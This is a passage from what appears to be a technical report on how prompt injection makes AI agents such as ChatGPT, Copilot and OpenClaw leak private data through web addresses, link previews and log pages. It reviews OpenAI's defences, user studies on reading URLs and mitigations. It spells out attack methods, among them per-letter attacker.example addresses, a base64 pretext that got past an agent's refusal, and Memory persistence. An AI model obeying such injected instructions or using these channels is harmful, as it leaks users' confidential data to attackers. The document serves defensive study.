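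It is also unclear whether the Gemini app itself always applies the provenance rule. *Gemini Agent Security Risks*, a 2026 rating by the security company Adversa AI, lists one-click leaks through links as a problem that Google has acknowledged but not fixed. Under the rule, Gemini should block any link to which the model has added private data. The rating cites other reports for this point, so it may describe Gemini before the rule, or a part of Gemini that the rule doesn't cover. A user can test a particular version by typing in an address and asking Gemini for a link to it with a dozen random digits added. If Gemini shows a working link, the rule isn't in force in that version.

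## ChatGPT: opening only addresses already public on the web

ChatGPT opens a web address by itself only if OpenAI's web crawler has already found that exact address on the public web. The crawler has no access to anyone's conversations, so an address containing a particular user's passport number should not be in its index. Unlike Gemini, ChatGPT doesn't accept an address just because it appears in the user's email, where an attacker could have put it. OpenAI took almost three years to arrive at this rule, and researchers got past several weaker checks during that time.

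### The first check, in December 2023

In April 2023, Johann Rehberger told OpenAI that ChatGPT would load an image from any address the model wrote, even if the address contained data from the conversation. OpenAI had no bug bounty programme at the time and, according to Embrace The Red, there was little interest in fixing the problem. OpenAI later added browsing, plugins and custom versions of ChatGPT called GPTs, which gave attackers more ways to inject prompts.

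That December, Rehberger demonstrated the theft live with a consenting victim. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* describes a change he noticed the next day. Before showing an image, ChatGPT's web page now sent the image's URL to an OpenAI service called `url_safe` and loaded the image only if the service approved. The service returned `{"safe":false}` for a URL with someone's email address in the query string.

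OpenAI didn't explain how the service decided which addresses to allow. Rehberger tried 36 addresses on his own site, one for each letter and digit, and nine of them passed. The image `a.png` loaded but `d.png` did not, for no apparent reason. Rehberger used two of the images to leak the word "hi", and wondered whether ChatGPT was looking addresses up in Bing's index. Nine images are enough to leak any text, though slowly, because two in a row have 9 × 9 = 81 combinations, more than enough for an alphabet of 36 characters.

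The check also worked only in apps that called it, so OpenAI had to add the call to each one. The web page had it, but the iPhone app didn't yet. Rehberger suggested checking on the server, which would protect all the apps at once, and allowing only one image or a handful per answer. Willison (2023), commenting on Rehberger's post, called the fix "half-baked" and expected attackers to get data past it in subdomains or file names.

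### Approved domains that let data out

`url_safe` checked individual addresses and also approved some entire domains. In October 2024, Rehberger reported several ways around the check, and later named two approved domains, windows.net and apache.org, where an outsider could read the server's logs. Microsoft rents out storage on windows.net, and each customer gets a subdomain and a log of requests to it.

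Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* describes an attack in which Rehberger rented some storage, then hid instructions in a PDF that made ChatGPT put the user's recent chat history into the address of an image in that storage. ChatGPT's program gave the model this history at the start of each new conversation, so one malicious document could expose unrelated conversations. The method still worked in 2025, months after the report.

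According to Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025), attackers could also get past the check because it always approved bing.com. Bing's search results use bing.com links that redirect to the actual pages, so any site in Bing's index can be reached through an approved address. Each link leads to one fixed page, so an attacker can't add a secret to it and would presumably need a separate page for each letter. OpenAI acknowledged the report in December 2024, but the flaw was still open in March 2025, after Tenable had asked about it six times.

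OpenAI tightened the check in the summer of 2025. Tenable had reported that links could open ChatGPT with a question already filled in and sent, and on July 11 OpenAI told Tenable that it had improved the feature. The problem, described in Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT Prompt Injection via ?q= Parameter in Web Interface* (2025), resembles the one that Varonis later found in Copilot's search page. According to Embrace The Red, further changes around August stopped Rehberger's attacks. By then, the web page had also stopped making a visible call to `url_safe`, so OpenAI had probably moved the check to its servers.

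### ShadowLeak: a request from OpenAI's own servers

These checks covered links and images in ChatGPT's answers. In June 2025, the security company Radware found that Deep Research, a ChatGPT agent, could open addresses without any comparable restriction. Deep Research writes a report after spending 5 to 30 minutes reading web pages and, if the user allows it, email. It opens the pages from OpenAI's servers, not the user's browser.

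Radware's *ShadowLeak* describes an attack that began with an email to the victim. Hidden instructions in it told the agent to find an employee's name and home address in another message and add them to a web address on Radware's server. When the victim asked the agent to research the day's emails about a new employee, the agent opened that address. The victim saw nothing, and the request never crossed the employer's network, so the filters there couldn't have caught it.

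Radware needed many attempts because the agent refused plain requests to send personal data and searched online for the unfamiliar address instead of opening it. Radware then learned the name of the tool for opening pages by asking the agent about its tools and reading the reasoning that ChatGPT displayed. Instructions that named the tool and called for retries worked some of the time. The attack became reliable only when Radware told the agent to encode the data in base64, supposedly for security. According to Radware, the model accepted this pretext, and the software carrying out the request then received a harmless-looking string. If that is right, OpenAI's defence relied partly on checking addresses for personal data, which encoding defeats.

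Radware reports a 100% success rate in repeated tests. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reproduces part of what is plainly the same email and reports a 50% success rate. Neither company gives the number of trials. The two figures may come from different versions of ChatGPT, or from different versions of the email, since Radware published it as one of several that worked. Even a 50% success rate is alarming for an attack that requires only one email.

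Radware reported the flaw on June 18. OpenAI fixed it in early August without telling Radware and acknowledged it on September 3. Radware published its advisory, *ShadowLeak* (2025), two weeks later.

### ZombieAgent: spelling out a secret with fixed addresses

After ShadowLeak, ChatGPT opened addresses only exactly as someone had provided them and refused to add anything to them, even when told to. On September 26, eight days after the advisory, Radware's Zvika Babo reported to OpenAI a way to bypass this restriction.

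As Radware's *ZombieAgent* explains, the attacker's email supplied a finished address for each letter and digit and one for the space. ChatGPT then spelled out the secret by opening them in order, as Copilot Chat did with images in CamoLeak. With an invented domain, the name Hannah would produce these requests:

```
https://attacker.example/h
https://attacker.example/a
https://attacker.example/n
https://attacker.example/n
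https://attacker.example/a
https://attacker.example/h
```

ChatGPT copied every address unchanged, so the new restriction had no effect. Radware also prepared a separate set of addresses for each position in the text, so that `h0` meant an *h* in the first position and `h5` an *h* in the sixth. The attacker could then reconstruct the text even if the requests arrived out of order. A text of up to 20 letters and digits needs 36 × 20 = 720 addresses, which a short program can generate.

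Radware also made the leak persist across conversations by using Memory, the ChatGPT feature that stores facts about the user. OpenAI had blocked ChatGPT from using Memory in a chat that had already used a connected service such as Gmail, and from opening an attacker's addresses stored in Memory. But ChatGPT could still read Memory first and Gmail afterwards. Instructions in a file that the user shared once could therefore make ChatGPT save a rule in Memory to look up a certain email before every reply. That email contained the attacker's addresses.

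In another demonstration, ChatGPT leaked email addresses from the victim's inbox, and the attacker's server sent the same malicious email to each address. Radware (2026) warned that this could start a "worm-like" campaign. Radware sells protection against such attacks, and its evidence came from its own demonstrations.

OpenAI fixed the flaw on December 16, 81 days after the report, and Radware published it on January 8, 2026. According to *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, a January 2026 news article, OpenAI stopped ChatGPT from opening links in emails unless they appeared in a well-known public index. This restriction would have blocked Radware's addresses if they existed only in the attacker's email.

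### How the public-address index works

OpenAI explained the rule on January 28, 2026, in a blog post and a paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*. The crawler builds an index of addresses on public pages, much as a search engine does. When an agent is about to load a page or image by itself, the program looks up the full address in the index. If the address is there, the agent may load the page or image. Otherwise, the program either tells the agent to try another website or warns the user and lets them decide. Embrace The Red describes an exception in which ChatGPT treats an address as safe for the rest of the chat if the user includes it in a message.

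The table applies the rule to some typical cases.

| Address | In the index? | What happens |
|---|---|---|
| A month-old newspaper article | Very likely | The agent opens it |
| `https://attacker.example/?d=X4419027`, which the model composed | No | The agent tries another site, or the user decides |
| `https://attacker.example/h`, which appears only in an email | No | The agent tries another site, or the user decides |
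| The same address, after the attacker has linked to it from a public page | Yes, once the crawler has found it | The agent opens it |
| A private document that a colleague has shared by link | No | The agent tries another site, or the user decides |
| An address that the user typed | It makes no difference | The agent opens it |

One of OpenAI's two reasons for not relying on a list of trusted sites is that many trustworthy sites have redirects, which an attacker could use against ChatGPT, as Tenable's Bing links had shown. Looking up the exact address handles redirects much better. The server at an indexed address can still redirect the agent anywhere, but the address contained no secret when the agent opened it, so the redirect has none to pass on.

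The other reason is that people visit far more sites than any list can hold. A strict list would set off many false alarms, and OpenAI expects users would learn to click through them without thinking. With an index, the agent can open an obscure blog as easily as a famous newspaper, as long as the crawler has visited it.

OpenAI promises only that the agent won't quietly leak the user's data through the address of a page it opens. It doesn't promise that the page is truthful, free of injected instructions or safe from attempts to manipulate the reader. The crawler also records phishing pages, so the rule would let the agent open them.

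Private data can still leak through public addresses, which OpenAI describes only as "much less likely" to contain it. An attacker could publish a page with a link for every common first name, such as `https://attacker.example/?name=hannah`. Once the crawler has recorded these links, ChatGPT can reveal the user's name by opening the one that matches.

### How much the choice of address can reveal

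The size of this leak depends on how many addresses the attacker has in the index and how many the agent opens. Suppose there are *N* addresses and the agent makes *k* fetches. Each fetch can go to any of the *N*, which gives *N*ᵏ possible sequences, so the attacker learns at most

*k* × log₂ *N* bits.

With 36 addresses, one fetch carries log₂ 36 = 5.17 bits, so ten fetches carry 51.7 bits, enough to encode any string of ten letters and digits.

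Many secrets contain less information than their length suggests. A passport number like X4419027, with one letter and seven digits, has 26 × 10⁷ possible values, or just under 28 bits. Spelling it out takes eight fetches, but six would be enough if the model first converted the number to base 36, because seven of the eight characters can only be digits. Embrace The Red points out that a larger website probably has 36 indexed pages already, and that an attacker could use thousands. The next table gives the fewest fetches that could transmit three kinds of secret.

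| Secret | Size | 36 addresses | 1,000 addresses | 1,000,000 addresses |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Answer to a yes-or-no question | 1 bit | 1 | 1 | 1 |
| Passport number | 28 bits | 6 | 3 | 2 |
| Random 20-character key | 119 bits | 24 | 12 | 6 |

Doubling the number of addresses adds only one bit per fetch. To send the same data in half as many fetches, the attacker has to square the number of addresses. For example, matching in five fetches what ten could carry with 36 addresses requires 36² = 1,296 addresses in the index.

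### Caching, repeat visits and a cap on fetches

Rehberger proposed a ban on repeat visits. He also proposed that ChatGPT keep a copy of each page for a few minutes and use it if the agent returns to the same address. Either addition would disrupt the simple letter-by-letter method. For the name Hannah, the attacker would log only *h*, *a* and *n*, because the other three requests would never leave OpenAI's servers.

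But an attacker who plans for this loses very little. If each address works only once, the first fetch has 36 options, the next has 35, and so on. Ten fetches then allow 36 × 35 × … × 27 sequences, about 9.2 × 10¹⁴, compared with 3.7 × 10¹⁵ when repeats are possible. The leak falls by only two bits. Limiting the number of fetches does much more:

| Limit, with 36 addresses | Most the attacker can learn |
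|---|---|
| Ten fetches, repeats allowed | 51.7 bits |
| Ten fetches, no repeats | 49.7 bits |
| Ten fetches, no repeats, order unknown | 27.9 bits |
| Five fetches, repeats allowed | 25.8 bits |
| Three fetches, repeats allowed | 15.5 bits |
| One fetch | 5.2 bits |

Losing the order of requests matters more than losing the repeats. Rehberger noticed in 2023 that image requests could arrive out of order because a browser may load several at once. An agent that opens pages one after another lacks this protection because its requests arrive in order.

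Radware's numbered addresses get around both obstacles. In `h0`, `a1`, `n2`, `n3`, `a4` and `h5`, no address repeats and each one includes its position. Covering ten positions takes 360 addresses, and ten fetches again carry the full 51.7 bits. Rehberger's additions would still help, because the attacker would have to get ten times as many pages into the index and the crudest attacks would fail. Rehberger acknowledged that some data could still leak, and had not tested whether OpenAI already did something similar.

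The cap also resembles Rehberger's 2023 suggestion to limit the number of images in an answer. Limiting images would inconvenience users very little, but a cap of three pages would make Deep Research useless, because its purpose is to read many pages. A more practical version would limit the number of pages the agent opens on any one unfamiliar site after it has read private data. The attacker could spread the alphabet over several sites, but would then need indexed pages on all of them.

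A cap for each conversation also has to account for Memory, because if an attack like ZombieAgent runs in every new chat, the attacker gets a new allowance each time. With three fetches per chat and 36 addresses, the 20-character key would leak in eight chats.

OpenAI could close this channel completely by giving the agent the crawler's stored copy of a page instead of opening the live one. The attacker's server would then receive no request, no matter which address the model chose, but stored pages go out of date.

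### Harmless pages that the index lacks

A link to a shared document usually contains a long random code and works for anyone who has it, so its owner keeps it off the public web. If a colleague emails such a link and the user asks ChatGPT to read the document, the lookup will fail even though the link is harmless. The agent can't find the document on another website, so the user has to approve the link or paste it into the chat. Gemini's rule handles this case better because it would match the address to the one in the email.

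New pages are also a problem, because they aren't in the index until the crawler finds them. The agent can often find another report of a news story, but there may be no good substitute for a company's new security notice. Addresses with many possible query strings are harder still. A railway website may have a different address for every combination of stations, date and time, which is far too many for a crawler to collect.

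OpenAI objected to trusted lists because people who see too many warnings stop reading them. False alarms could cause the same problem here, though a large, frequently updated index should produce fewer of them than a short list would. OpenAI's post gives no figures for how often ChatGPT shows the warning or how users respond, so it is hard to tell how well the company has avoided the problem.

### Features that bypass the check

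Finally, Rehberger worried that some OpenAI developers might not know about the check and might build features without it. This had happened before. The iPhone and Mac apps lacked `url_safe` at first, and Deep Research could open any address when Radware tested it.

By March 2026, OpenAI had extended the check, now called Safe Url, to searches and page visits in Deep Research and to page visits and bookmarks in Atlas, its browser. Small applications that ChatGPT builds or runs in its Canvas and Apps features have a separate protection, a sandbox that detects unexpected communication and asks the user for consent. OpenAI says that its safety training leads the model to refuse most of the attacks the company knows of, and that Safe Url is for the rest.

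An August 2026 experiment, reported in *The Framing Gap* (2026), fits this account but can't confirm it. Researchers hid instructions in outside content to make agents disclose a secret they had been told to protect. The attacks succeeded up to 100% of the time against a model accessed through OpenAI's API, but in none of 48 valid trials against ChatGPT. The researchers couldn't see inside ChatGPT and did not attribute the difference to any particular defence. No successes in 48 trials is also compatible with a true success rate as high as about 6%.

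Images and links copied from a web page remained a weak point in 2026. The Hacker News (2026) reported in May on ChatGPhish, an attack that the security company Permiso found. When ChatGPT summarised a page containing the attacker's Markdown, it loaded the attacker's images automatically and showed the attacker's links as clickable. The index may still have worked as intended, since the rule would allow the image request if the crawler had already recorded the address. OpenAI never promised that the links on a page would be safe to follow.

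Data can also leak without a web address for the check to inspect. In March 2026, Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* described a hidden connection to the public internet from the isolated environment where ChatGPT runs code. A single malicious prompt could leak messages and uploaded files through this connection. As with the code attack on Copilot, a better link check would not prevent this.

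### Lockdown Mode: reading stored pages only

In February 2026, OpenAI introduced Lockdown Mode, an optional setting that limits the agent's browsing to cached pages. According to OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026), "no live network requests leave OpenAI's controlled network" in this mode. An attacker therefore cannot use a set of indexed addresses, each standing for a letter, to spell out private data, because opening a page sends nothing to its owner. OpenAI first offered Lockdown Mode only to organisations such as companies and schools, then began offering it for personal accounts on June 4.

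This protection considerably limits what users can do with ChatGPT. OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*, a help page that the company was still updating in December 2026, warns that search results may be out of date or missing. The mode turns off Deep Research and the agent that performs tasks on websites, and ChatGPT may not show images in ordinary answers. It doesn't affect Memory or file uploads, and it doesn't restrict network access in Codex, OpenAI's programming assistant.

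Willison (2026) concluded from the existence of Lockdown Mode that ChatGPT's default settings don't give robust protection against a determined attacker. OpenAI's head of security, Dane Stuckey, described Lockdown Mode as a tool for people at elevated risk, for whom losing features is worthwhile. Willison's inference seems right, because a choice among indexed addresses can reveal so much. For most people, though, an attack that first requires dozens of indexed pages is a smaller danger than the one-line leaks of 2023.

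ChatGPT can write a web page and preview it in a sandbox that blocks contact with outside servers unless the user consents. The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026) reports that Check Point found that, even in Lockdown Mode, such a page could open a popup window outside the sandbox, where the restrictions did not apply. In the desktop app, this could leak chat data without a click. An attacker could deliver the page through a crafted prompt, a malicious GPT or a shared chat. OpenAI fixed the flaw on September 18, and Check Point published it in November.

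A week earlier, another company, Parameter Labs, had described a separate flaw in the same preview feature. A victim who opened an attacker's shared chat and clicked the preview once could lose control of their account. Both flaws were in a feature that displays pages, not in the tools that fetch them, and neither involved the index.

On its help page, OpenAI doesn't guarantee that Lockdown Mode prevents every leak. It lists connected apps, unforeseen combinations of features and new techniques as remaining risks. In workplaces that manage their own settings, the mode doesn't switch off every app automatically. OpenAI advises administrators not to let an app write or post anything unless they can confirm that an attacker couldn't see the result.

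## Link previews and log pages: when another program opens the address

An agent that posts in a private Slack channel can leak data even if no outsider can read the channel. Slack's servers open the links in a message to build previews, so if the agent has put a secret in a link to an attacker's server, the preview request delivers the secret to that server. An administrator who takes OpenAI's advice might still allow these posts because the channel is private.

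Even if the agent's own program handles a link safely, for example by showing the address as plain text, data can leak when a second program displays the same text under different rules. Similarly, an application can block a malicious image and still leak the data when one of its developers opens the stored answer on a log page.

### How a preview sends the data

A link preview shows a page's title, and often a picture, below the message that links to it. Messaging apps introduced previews for links that people chose to share. When an agent writes the link, the app may open it before anyone has looked at the address.

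Johann Rehberger warned of this in August 2024, in Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* ("unfurling" is Slack's word for building a preview). He posted a link to his own website through a Slack app, and the site's log showed a request from a program called Slackbot-LinkExpanding. He also gave an example injection that makes a chatbot write an address ending with the text of the conversation's first message. Slack would open that address immediately, whereas the link that Slack AI had labelled "click here to reauthenticate" leaked data only when the victim clicked it. Willison (2024), in a note with the same title, described this as a vulnerability he "hadn't thought about before".

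As in ShadowLeak, the request never crosses the employer's network. An attacker can also use invisible characters to hide the data from anyone who reads the link in the chat.

A Slack app can turn previews off for each message it posts, using two settings:

```
"unfurl_links": false,
"unfurl_media": false
```

The first setting covers pages that are mainly text, and the second covers images, video and audio. According to Slack's *Unfurling links in messages*, the company's servers have to fetch every address to find out what kind of content it leads to. An app that turns off only one setting would therefore presumably still leak data through that request. To stop Slack from opening links, the app has to set both to false.

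Slack never shows a preview if the link text is part of the address, such as "example.com" for a link to that site. This exception offers little protection, because an attacker can have the model use different link text. Slack now suggests that developers consider turning previews off for messages from a language model, but previews remain on by default.

### A private channel that leaked

In 2025 Rehberger found the problem in a small, widely used Anthropic program that let AI agents read and post Slack messages. The program was a server for the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard way to connect AI models to outside tools. Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory* explains that a company could restrict the program to posting in a single private channel. Users then had a good reason to let the agent post without approving each message, because the worst outcome seemed to be a strange message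 that only colleagues would read.

In one demonstration, a user asked Claude to analyse a document and post a summary for the team. The document contained instructions to add the latest message from another channel to a link in the post. Claude posted the link in the private channel, as its permissions allowed, and Slack's request for a link preview sent the message to Rehberger's server. In a second demonstration, instructions written in invisible characters in a source code file leaked a developer's API key the same way.

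Rehberger told Anthropic about the flaw on May 27, 2025. Anthropic archived the program two days later, though it isn't clear that the report was the reason. It had no plans to release a patch, so anyone who kept using the program had to add Slack's two settings to the code themselves. People were still downloading it more than 14,000 times a week. Rehberger recommends that every program of this kind turn previews off by default, and suggests a list of approved domains for companies that want to keep some previews.

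### OpenClaw on Telegram and other combinations

PromptArmor tested this weakness in a wider range of agents and apps in February 2026. Its *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* focuses on OpenClaw, an AI agent that people run themselves and control through messaging apps such as Telegram. By default, Telegram opened links in OpenClaw's messages, and PromptArmor's test site logged any data in the address. The requests stopped after the user added `linkPreview: false` to the Telegram section of OpenClaw's configuration file.

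The test site was open to the public. It recorded each preview request along with the data in the address. Visitors could state which agent and app had caused a request, and could also report combinations that had caused none. Apostol's *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews* reports that data leaked from agents built with Microsoft's Copilot Studio when they ran in Teams, and from certain bots in Slack. It also lists Discord as an affected platform.

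Results from volunteers can show that a combination leaks, but not how common such leaks are. A combination reported as safe may simply have had its previews turned off. The public test also measured only whether the app would open a link in an agent's message. An attacker would first have to get the agent to write that link.

OpenClaw has since changed its defaults for Slack, but not for Telegram. In a test release in May 2026, it added separate settings for Slack's link and media previews, so that users could turn them off for the agent without changing the whole workspace. By October, the *Slack* page of OpenClaw's manual listed link previews as off by default but gave no default for media previews. Since Slack may open a link unless both settings are off, users should turn off media previews themselves.

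On Telegram, where PromptArmor had demonstrated the leak, previews were still on by default in August 2026, according to OpenClaw's *Telegram*. This default is hard to justify, because without previews the user loses only a title and a thumbnail, and an agent that has just read a page can put the title in its message anyway.

Copilot Cowork could leak file links through images in Teams messages as well as in emails, according to PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files*.

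### A blocked image in OpenAI's logs

Many companies build AI features on OpenAI's API, which lets their programs send text to OpenAI's models and receive answers. OpenAI also gives developers a web page for viewing past conversations. PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs* shows how this page could leak data from an application that had blocked an attack.

PromptArmor built a mock version of a tool that banks use to verify their customers' identities. Such a tool has to combine confidential documents with whatever it can find about the customer online. The attack went as follows:

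1. The tool collected six sources on a customer. One contained text from the web in which an attacker had planted instructions.
2. A user of the tool chose one of its suggested questions.
3. The model followed the instructions and wrote a Markdown image with the customer's data in its address.
4. A second model, which checked the answers, flagged this one, and the tool didn't display it.
5. A developer opened the flagged conversation in OpenAI's log viewer to find out what had happened.
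6. The log viewer treated the stored answer as Markdown, so the developer's browser requested the image and sent the data to the attacker.

In the demonstration, the attacker's log contained identity documents and financial details. The customer had done nothing, and the user of the tool never saw the image. The check in step 4 worked, but it made the leak more likely because it gave a developer a reason to open that conversation.

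Other defences in the application, such as using a CSP, removing the image with a sanitizer or showing all answers as plain text, would have failed in the same way. They protect the user in the application but don't affect what OpenAI's log viewer does with the original answer. PromptArmor gives the example of the search assistant Perplexity, whose sanitizer removed an image and left an oddly empty answer. A user might well give such an answer a thumbs-down, which could lead a developer to look it up. PromptArmor didn't show that any data had leaked from Perplexity this way.

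The same fault appeared in other parts of OpenAI's platform. Three tools for building chats, assistants and agents loaded outside images in their preview windows, so a developer could leak data just by testing a product. ChatKit's starter app, which developers can use as a basis for their own chat programs, had no protection against such images either. That may be harder to fix than the log viewer, because OpenAI can change its own pages for everyone at once, but developers who have already built on the starter app may have to update their copies separately.

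PromptArmor reported the flaw on November 17, 2025, through Bugcrowd, a company that screens such reports for OpenAI. PromptArmor sent step-by-step instructions three days later and answered questions on three more days. On December 4, Bugcrowd closed the report as not applicable. PromptArmor acknowledges that flaws involving prompt injection are hard to sort into the existing categories. Still, a reviewer could see that a log page was loading images from unknown websites without settling any question about injection.

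PromptArmor then published its findings. OpenAI confirmed that the flaw was real and said it had not seen the original report because Bugcrowd had handled it. On January 22, 2026, OpenAI reopened the report and indicated that a fix was under way. PromptArmor's timeline ends there and doesn't record a completed fix. Developers can test for the flaw, using made-up data, by having a model write an image with an address on their own server and then opening the answer in the log viewer. If their server receives a request, the flaw is still there.

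OpenAI published its paper on the public-address index six days after reopening the report. The index determines which addresses an agent may open by itself, but in the log viewer the developer's browser made the request.

### Keeping the check with the text

An application's checks cover only the copy of an answer that the application displays. Preventing leaks elsewhere requires either repeating the check in every program that displays the answer or storing the answer in a form that no program will turn into a request.

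A company that checks addresses in one product can forget to do so in another. OpenAI began checking image addresses in ChatGPT in December 2023, but Rapid7's *CVE-2026-14898* describes a flaw in OpenAI's Codex app for macOS, which loaded outside images from the model's answers without a click. A prompt injection could have used these images to steal API keys or source code, though there are no known attacks.

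Removing unapproved addresses before storing the text protects every later display, including pages that nobody has built yet. But investigators need those addresses, which show what the attacker was after and where the data would have gone, so the program can keep them in a separate field that always appears as plain text. Storing a note that the answer failed a check isn't enough, because a log page that doesn't check for the note will still load the image. In PromptArmor's demonstration, only OpenAI could have cleaned the stored answer, because its log contained the model's original text and not the application's filtered version.

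Plain text suits a log page because a developer investigating a strange answer wants to see exactly what the model wrote, and rendered Markdown hides part of it. In messaging apps, however, plain text doesn't prevent the leak. The injection in Rehberger's 2024 example used a bare address with no Markdown, and Slack turns such an address into a link and opens it. Slack ignores addresses that don't start with `https://` or `http://`, so an agent's program could remove those characters, but other apps may be less strict.

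Turning previews off stops the automatic request but leaves the secret in the link, so the agent's program still needs to check the address.

A messaging app could also keep previews and check each address before opening it. Gemini's rule would be difficult to apply here, because Slack or Telegram usually doesn't have access to what the agent read before it wrote the link. A public-address index like OpenAI's and Rehberger's list of approved domains require only the address. Both would have the same weaknesses as elsewhere, such as approved domains that pass data on. Fetching previews through a proxy doesn't prevent leaks unless the proxy applies such a check. When Rehberger's test link led to an image, Slack's own image proxy made one of the requests and passed on the full address, including the secret.

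| Measure | Effect on link previews | Effect on log pages | Who controls it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Remove unapproved addresses before sending or storing | Prevents the leak | Prevents the leak | The agent's maker for messages, the log's operator for stored answers |
| Use plain text | None in most cases | Prevents the automatic request | The agent's maker for messages, the log's operator for its pages |
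| Turn previews off | Leaves a link that leaks if someone clicks it | None | The agent's maker for its own messages, an administrator for a workspace |
| Check each address before fetching it | Prevents most leaks | Prevents most leaks | The messaging app or the log's operator |

PromptArmor wants messaging apps to offer settings for link previews, and agent developers to use those settings or let users choose. Slack and Telegram already let an agent send messages without previews, so developers of agents for those two apps can turn previews off now.

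Administrators have less precise controls. They can turn previews off for a whole workspace, but then employees lose them too. They can also decide which apps employees may install and what each app may do. Slack's guide *Data & security best practices for agentic Slack apps* (Kemple, updated April 2026) advises companies to sort permissions by risk, and lists posting messages among those they can always allow. An agent that reads confidential files and posts with previews on can use that permission to send the files' contents to an attacker, though always allowing it is reasonable for a bot that only posts routine announcements.

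PromptArmor would also like messaging apps to let people turn previews off for a particular chat or channel, which would cover a case that settings on individual messages miss. If an agent posts a link with previews off and an employee copies it into a new message to ask a colleague about it, Slack treats the new message as an ordinary one from a person and opens the link. A channel-wide setting would prevent that, unless the employee asked in a different channel.

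## Showing people the full address before a link opens

With previews turned off, a link that contains private data doesn't send that data anywhere until someone clicks it. Before opening the link, a program can show the reader the full address and ask whether to continue. This works only if people look at the address and understand it, and research suggests that many do neither.

### The notices in ChatGPT and Colab

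ChatGPT can show a notice when a link's address isn't in OpenAI's index of public pages. The notice, titled "Check this link is safe", warns that the link isn't verified and may share data from the conversation with another site. It shows the address and lets the user copy the link or open it. OpenAI advises anyone who notices something odd to leave the link alone and ask ChatGPT for another source or a summary.

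The dialog correctly warns that opening the link could leak data. Someone who thinks only of fake websites might open a leaking link to see whether the page looks genuine, and opening it would send the data. But the user still has to find the private data in the address.

In its later post on Safe Url, OpenAI writes that ChatGPT may show the user "the information that would be transmitted" and ask for confirmation. This sounds more helpful than showing the address, because people can recognise their own phone number without knowing what a query string is. However, "the information" may just be the address in the dialog, because both posts describe the same check, and looking up an address in an index can't show which part of it is private.

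In Colab, Google asks users to confirm before a link in Gemini's answers opens. Embrace The Red's *Google Colab AI* (2024) explains that Colab puts `https://www.google.com/url?q=` in front of these links, so a click leads first to Google's confirmation page. According to Li (2020), large websites including Facebook and Microsoft have also sent clicks through their own pages for over a decade.

Rehberger found that Colab showed no confirmation page for links to Google's own domains. In his demonstration, an injection made Gemini ask for personal details and offer a link labelled "I'm feeling lucky". The link led to a program he had set up on Google's Apps Script service. Clicking it sent the program the user's name, email address and the source code from the open document. Google had made the same exception in Bard's image policy.

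### How people read addresses

Colab's prefix also makes every link's address begin with google.com, wherever the link leads. That could mislead people, because they tend to look for a familiar name. In *What is this URL's Destination?*, Albakry, Vaniea and Wolters (2020) showed 23 addresses to 1,929 people recruited online and asked where each would lead. Twelve tested whether people knew which part of a domain identifies its owner. For example, `https://profile.facebook.com` belongs to Facebook, but `https://facebook.profile.com` belongs to the owner of profile.com.

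On average, participants got 5.2 out of 6 right when the company's name was in the position that identifies the owner, and 1.2 out of 6 when the name came first. About a third chose the named company every time, and only 8% answered all twelve correctly. Experience helped a little. When the name came first, the most technical group got 25% right, compared with 16% for the least technical.

They did better with `https://facebook.com/?url=twitter`. About three quarters correctly said it would lead to Facebook, but they could get this right by ignoring everything after the domain, where a leaking link usually holds the data.

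Many people don't look at the address at all. In *Does Domain Highlighting Help People Identify Phishing Sites?*, Lin, Greenberg and colleagues (2011) showed 22 people 16 web pages, half of them fake, in a browser that displayed the domain in black and the rest of the address in grey. Participants rated the fake pages as safe 57% of the time, and still did so 44% of the time when the researchers told them to look at the address bar. Nine of the 22 judged pages entirely by their content, such as logos and security badges. In *Ineffectiveness of Domain Highlighting*, Xiong, Yang and colleagues (2016) ran a similar test online with 320 people and six pages.

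Participants in Lin's study knew they were judging safety, so people who are busy with something else would probably do worse, and they may not realise it. *Measuring Identity Confusion with Uniform Resource Locators* (Reynolds, Kumar and colleagues, 2020) found that people were confident they could identify a website from its address, but disguised addresses still fooled them.

### Warnings beside the link

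Warnings that are hard to miss can make a large difference. In *Put Your Warning Where Your Link Is*, Petelka, Zou and Schaub (2019) gave 701 people an inbox of ten emails, three with a phishing link, and asked them to check whether the links worked. In some versions, the researchers disabled the original link, so participants could continue only by clicking the address inside the warning.

| Warning | Phishing links clicked |
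|---|---|
| None | 77% |
| Banner above the email | 44% |
| Beside the link, always visible | 34% |
| Beside the link, on hover | 30% |
| Beside the link, always visible, original link disabled | 16% |
| Full page in the browser, after the click | 12% |
| Beside the link, on hover, original link disabled | 9% |

The full-page result may be inflated, because participants who reached that page could have concluded that the link didn't work. The warnings beside the link were also headed "Fake Website, Don't Click!" and were always right. A warning in ChatGPT can't be that definite when an address is only missing from an index.

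*Restricting the Link*, a follow-up by Petelka, Berens and colleagues, used the milder heading "This link might be dangerous!" and put the same warning on one harmless link. Among 1,320 participants, disabling the original link reduced clicks more than a delay of two to five seconds did, and combining the two worked best. But these measures also reduced clicks on the harmless link, so some participants may have been obeying the warning without judging the address.

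*URL Inspection Tasks* (Lain, Nakatsuka and colleagues, 2025) is the closest test of a dialog like ChatGPT's. Its 2,673 participants in the United States, Germany and Japan played office workers dealing with email. In the American sample of 1,573, people with no help fell for 74% of the phishing emails. A second group, who after each click saw a page that displayed the address and asked them to confirm, fell for 57%. They typically spent three seconds on that page, and almost the same time on phishing links as on genuine ones.

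A third group had to complete a task with the address, such as highlighting the domain or retyping it, and saw an error message if they got it wrong. They fell for only 35% of the phishing emails. The tasks typically took 6 to 10 seconds, and people opened fewer genuine links (82%, compared with 91% for those with no help). Lain and colleagues recommend using such tasks only occasionally.

A rate of 57% is discouraging for any dialog that only shows an address and asks for confirmation. ChatGPT's dialog may do better because it gives a reason for concern and doesn't appear for every link.

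### How far the phishing research applies

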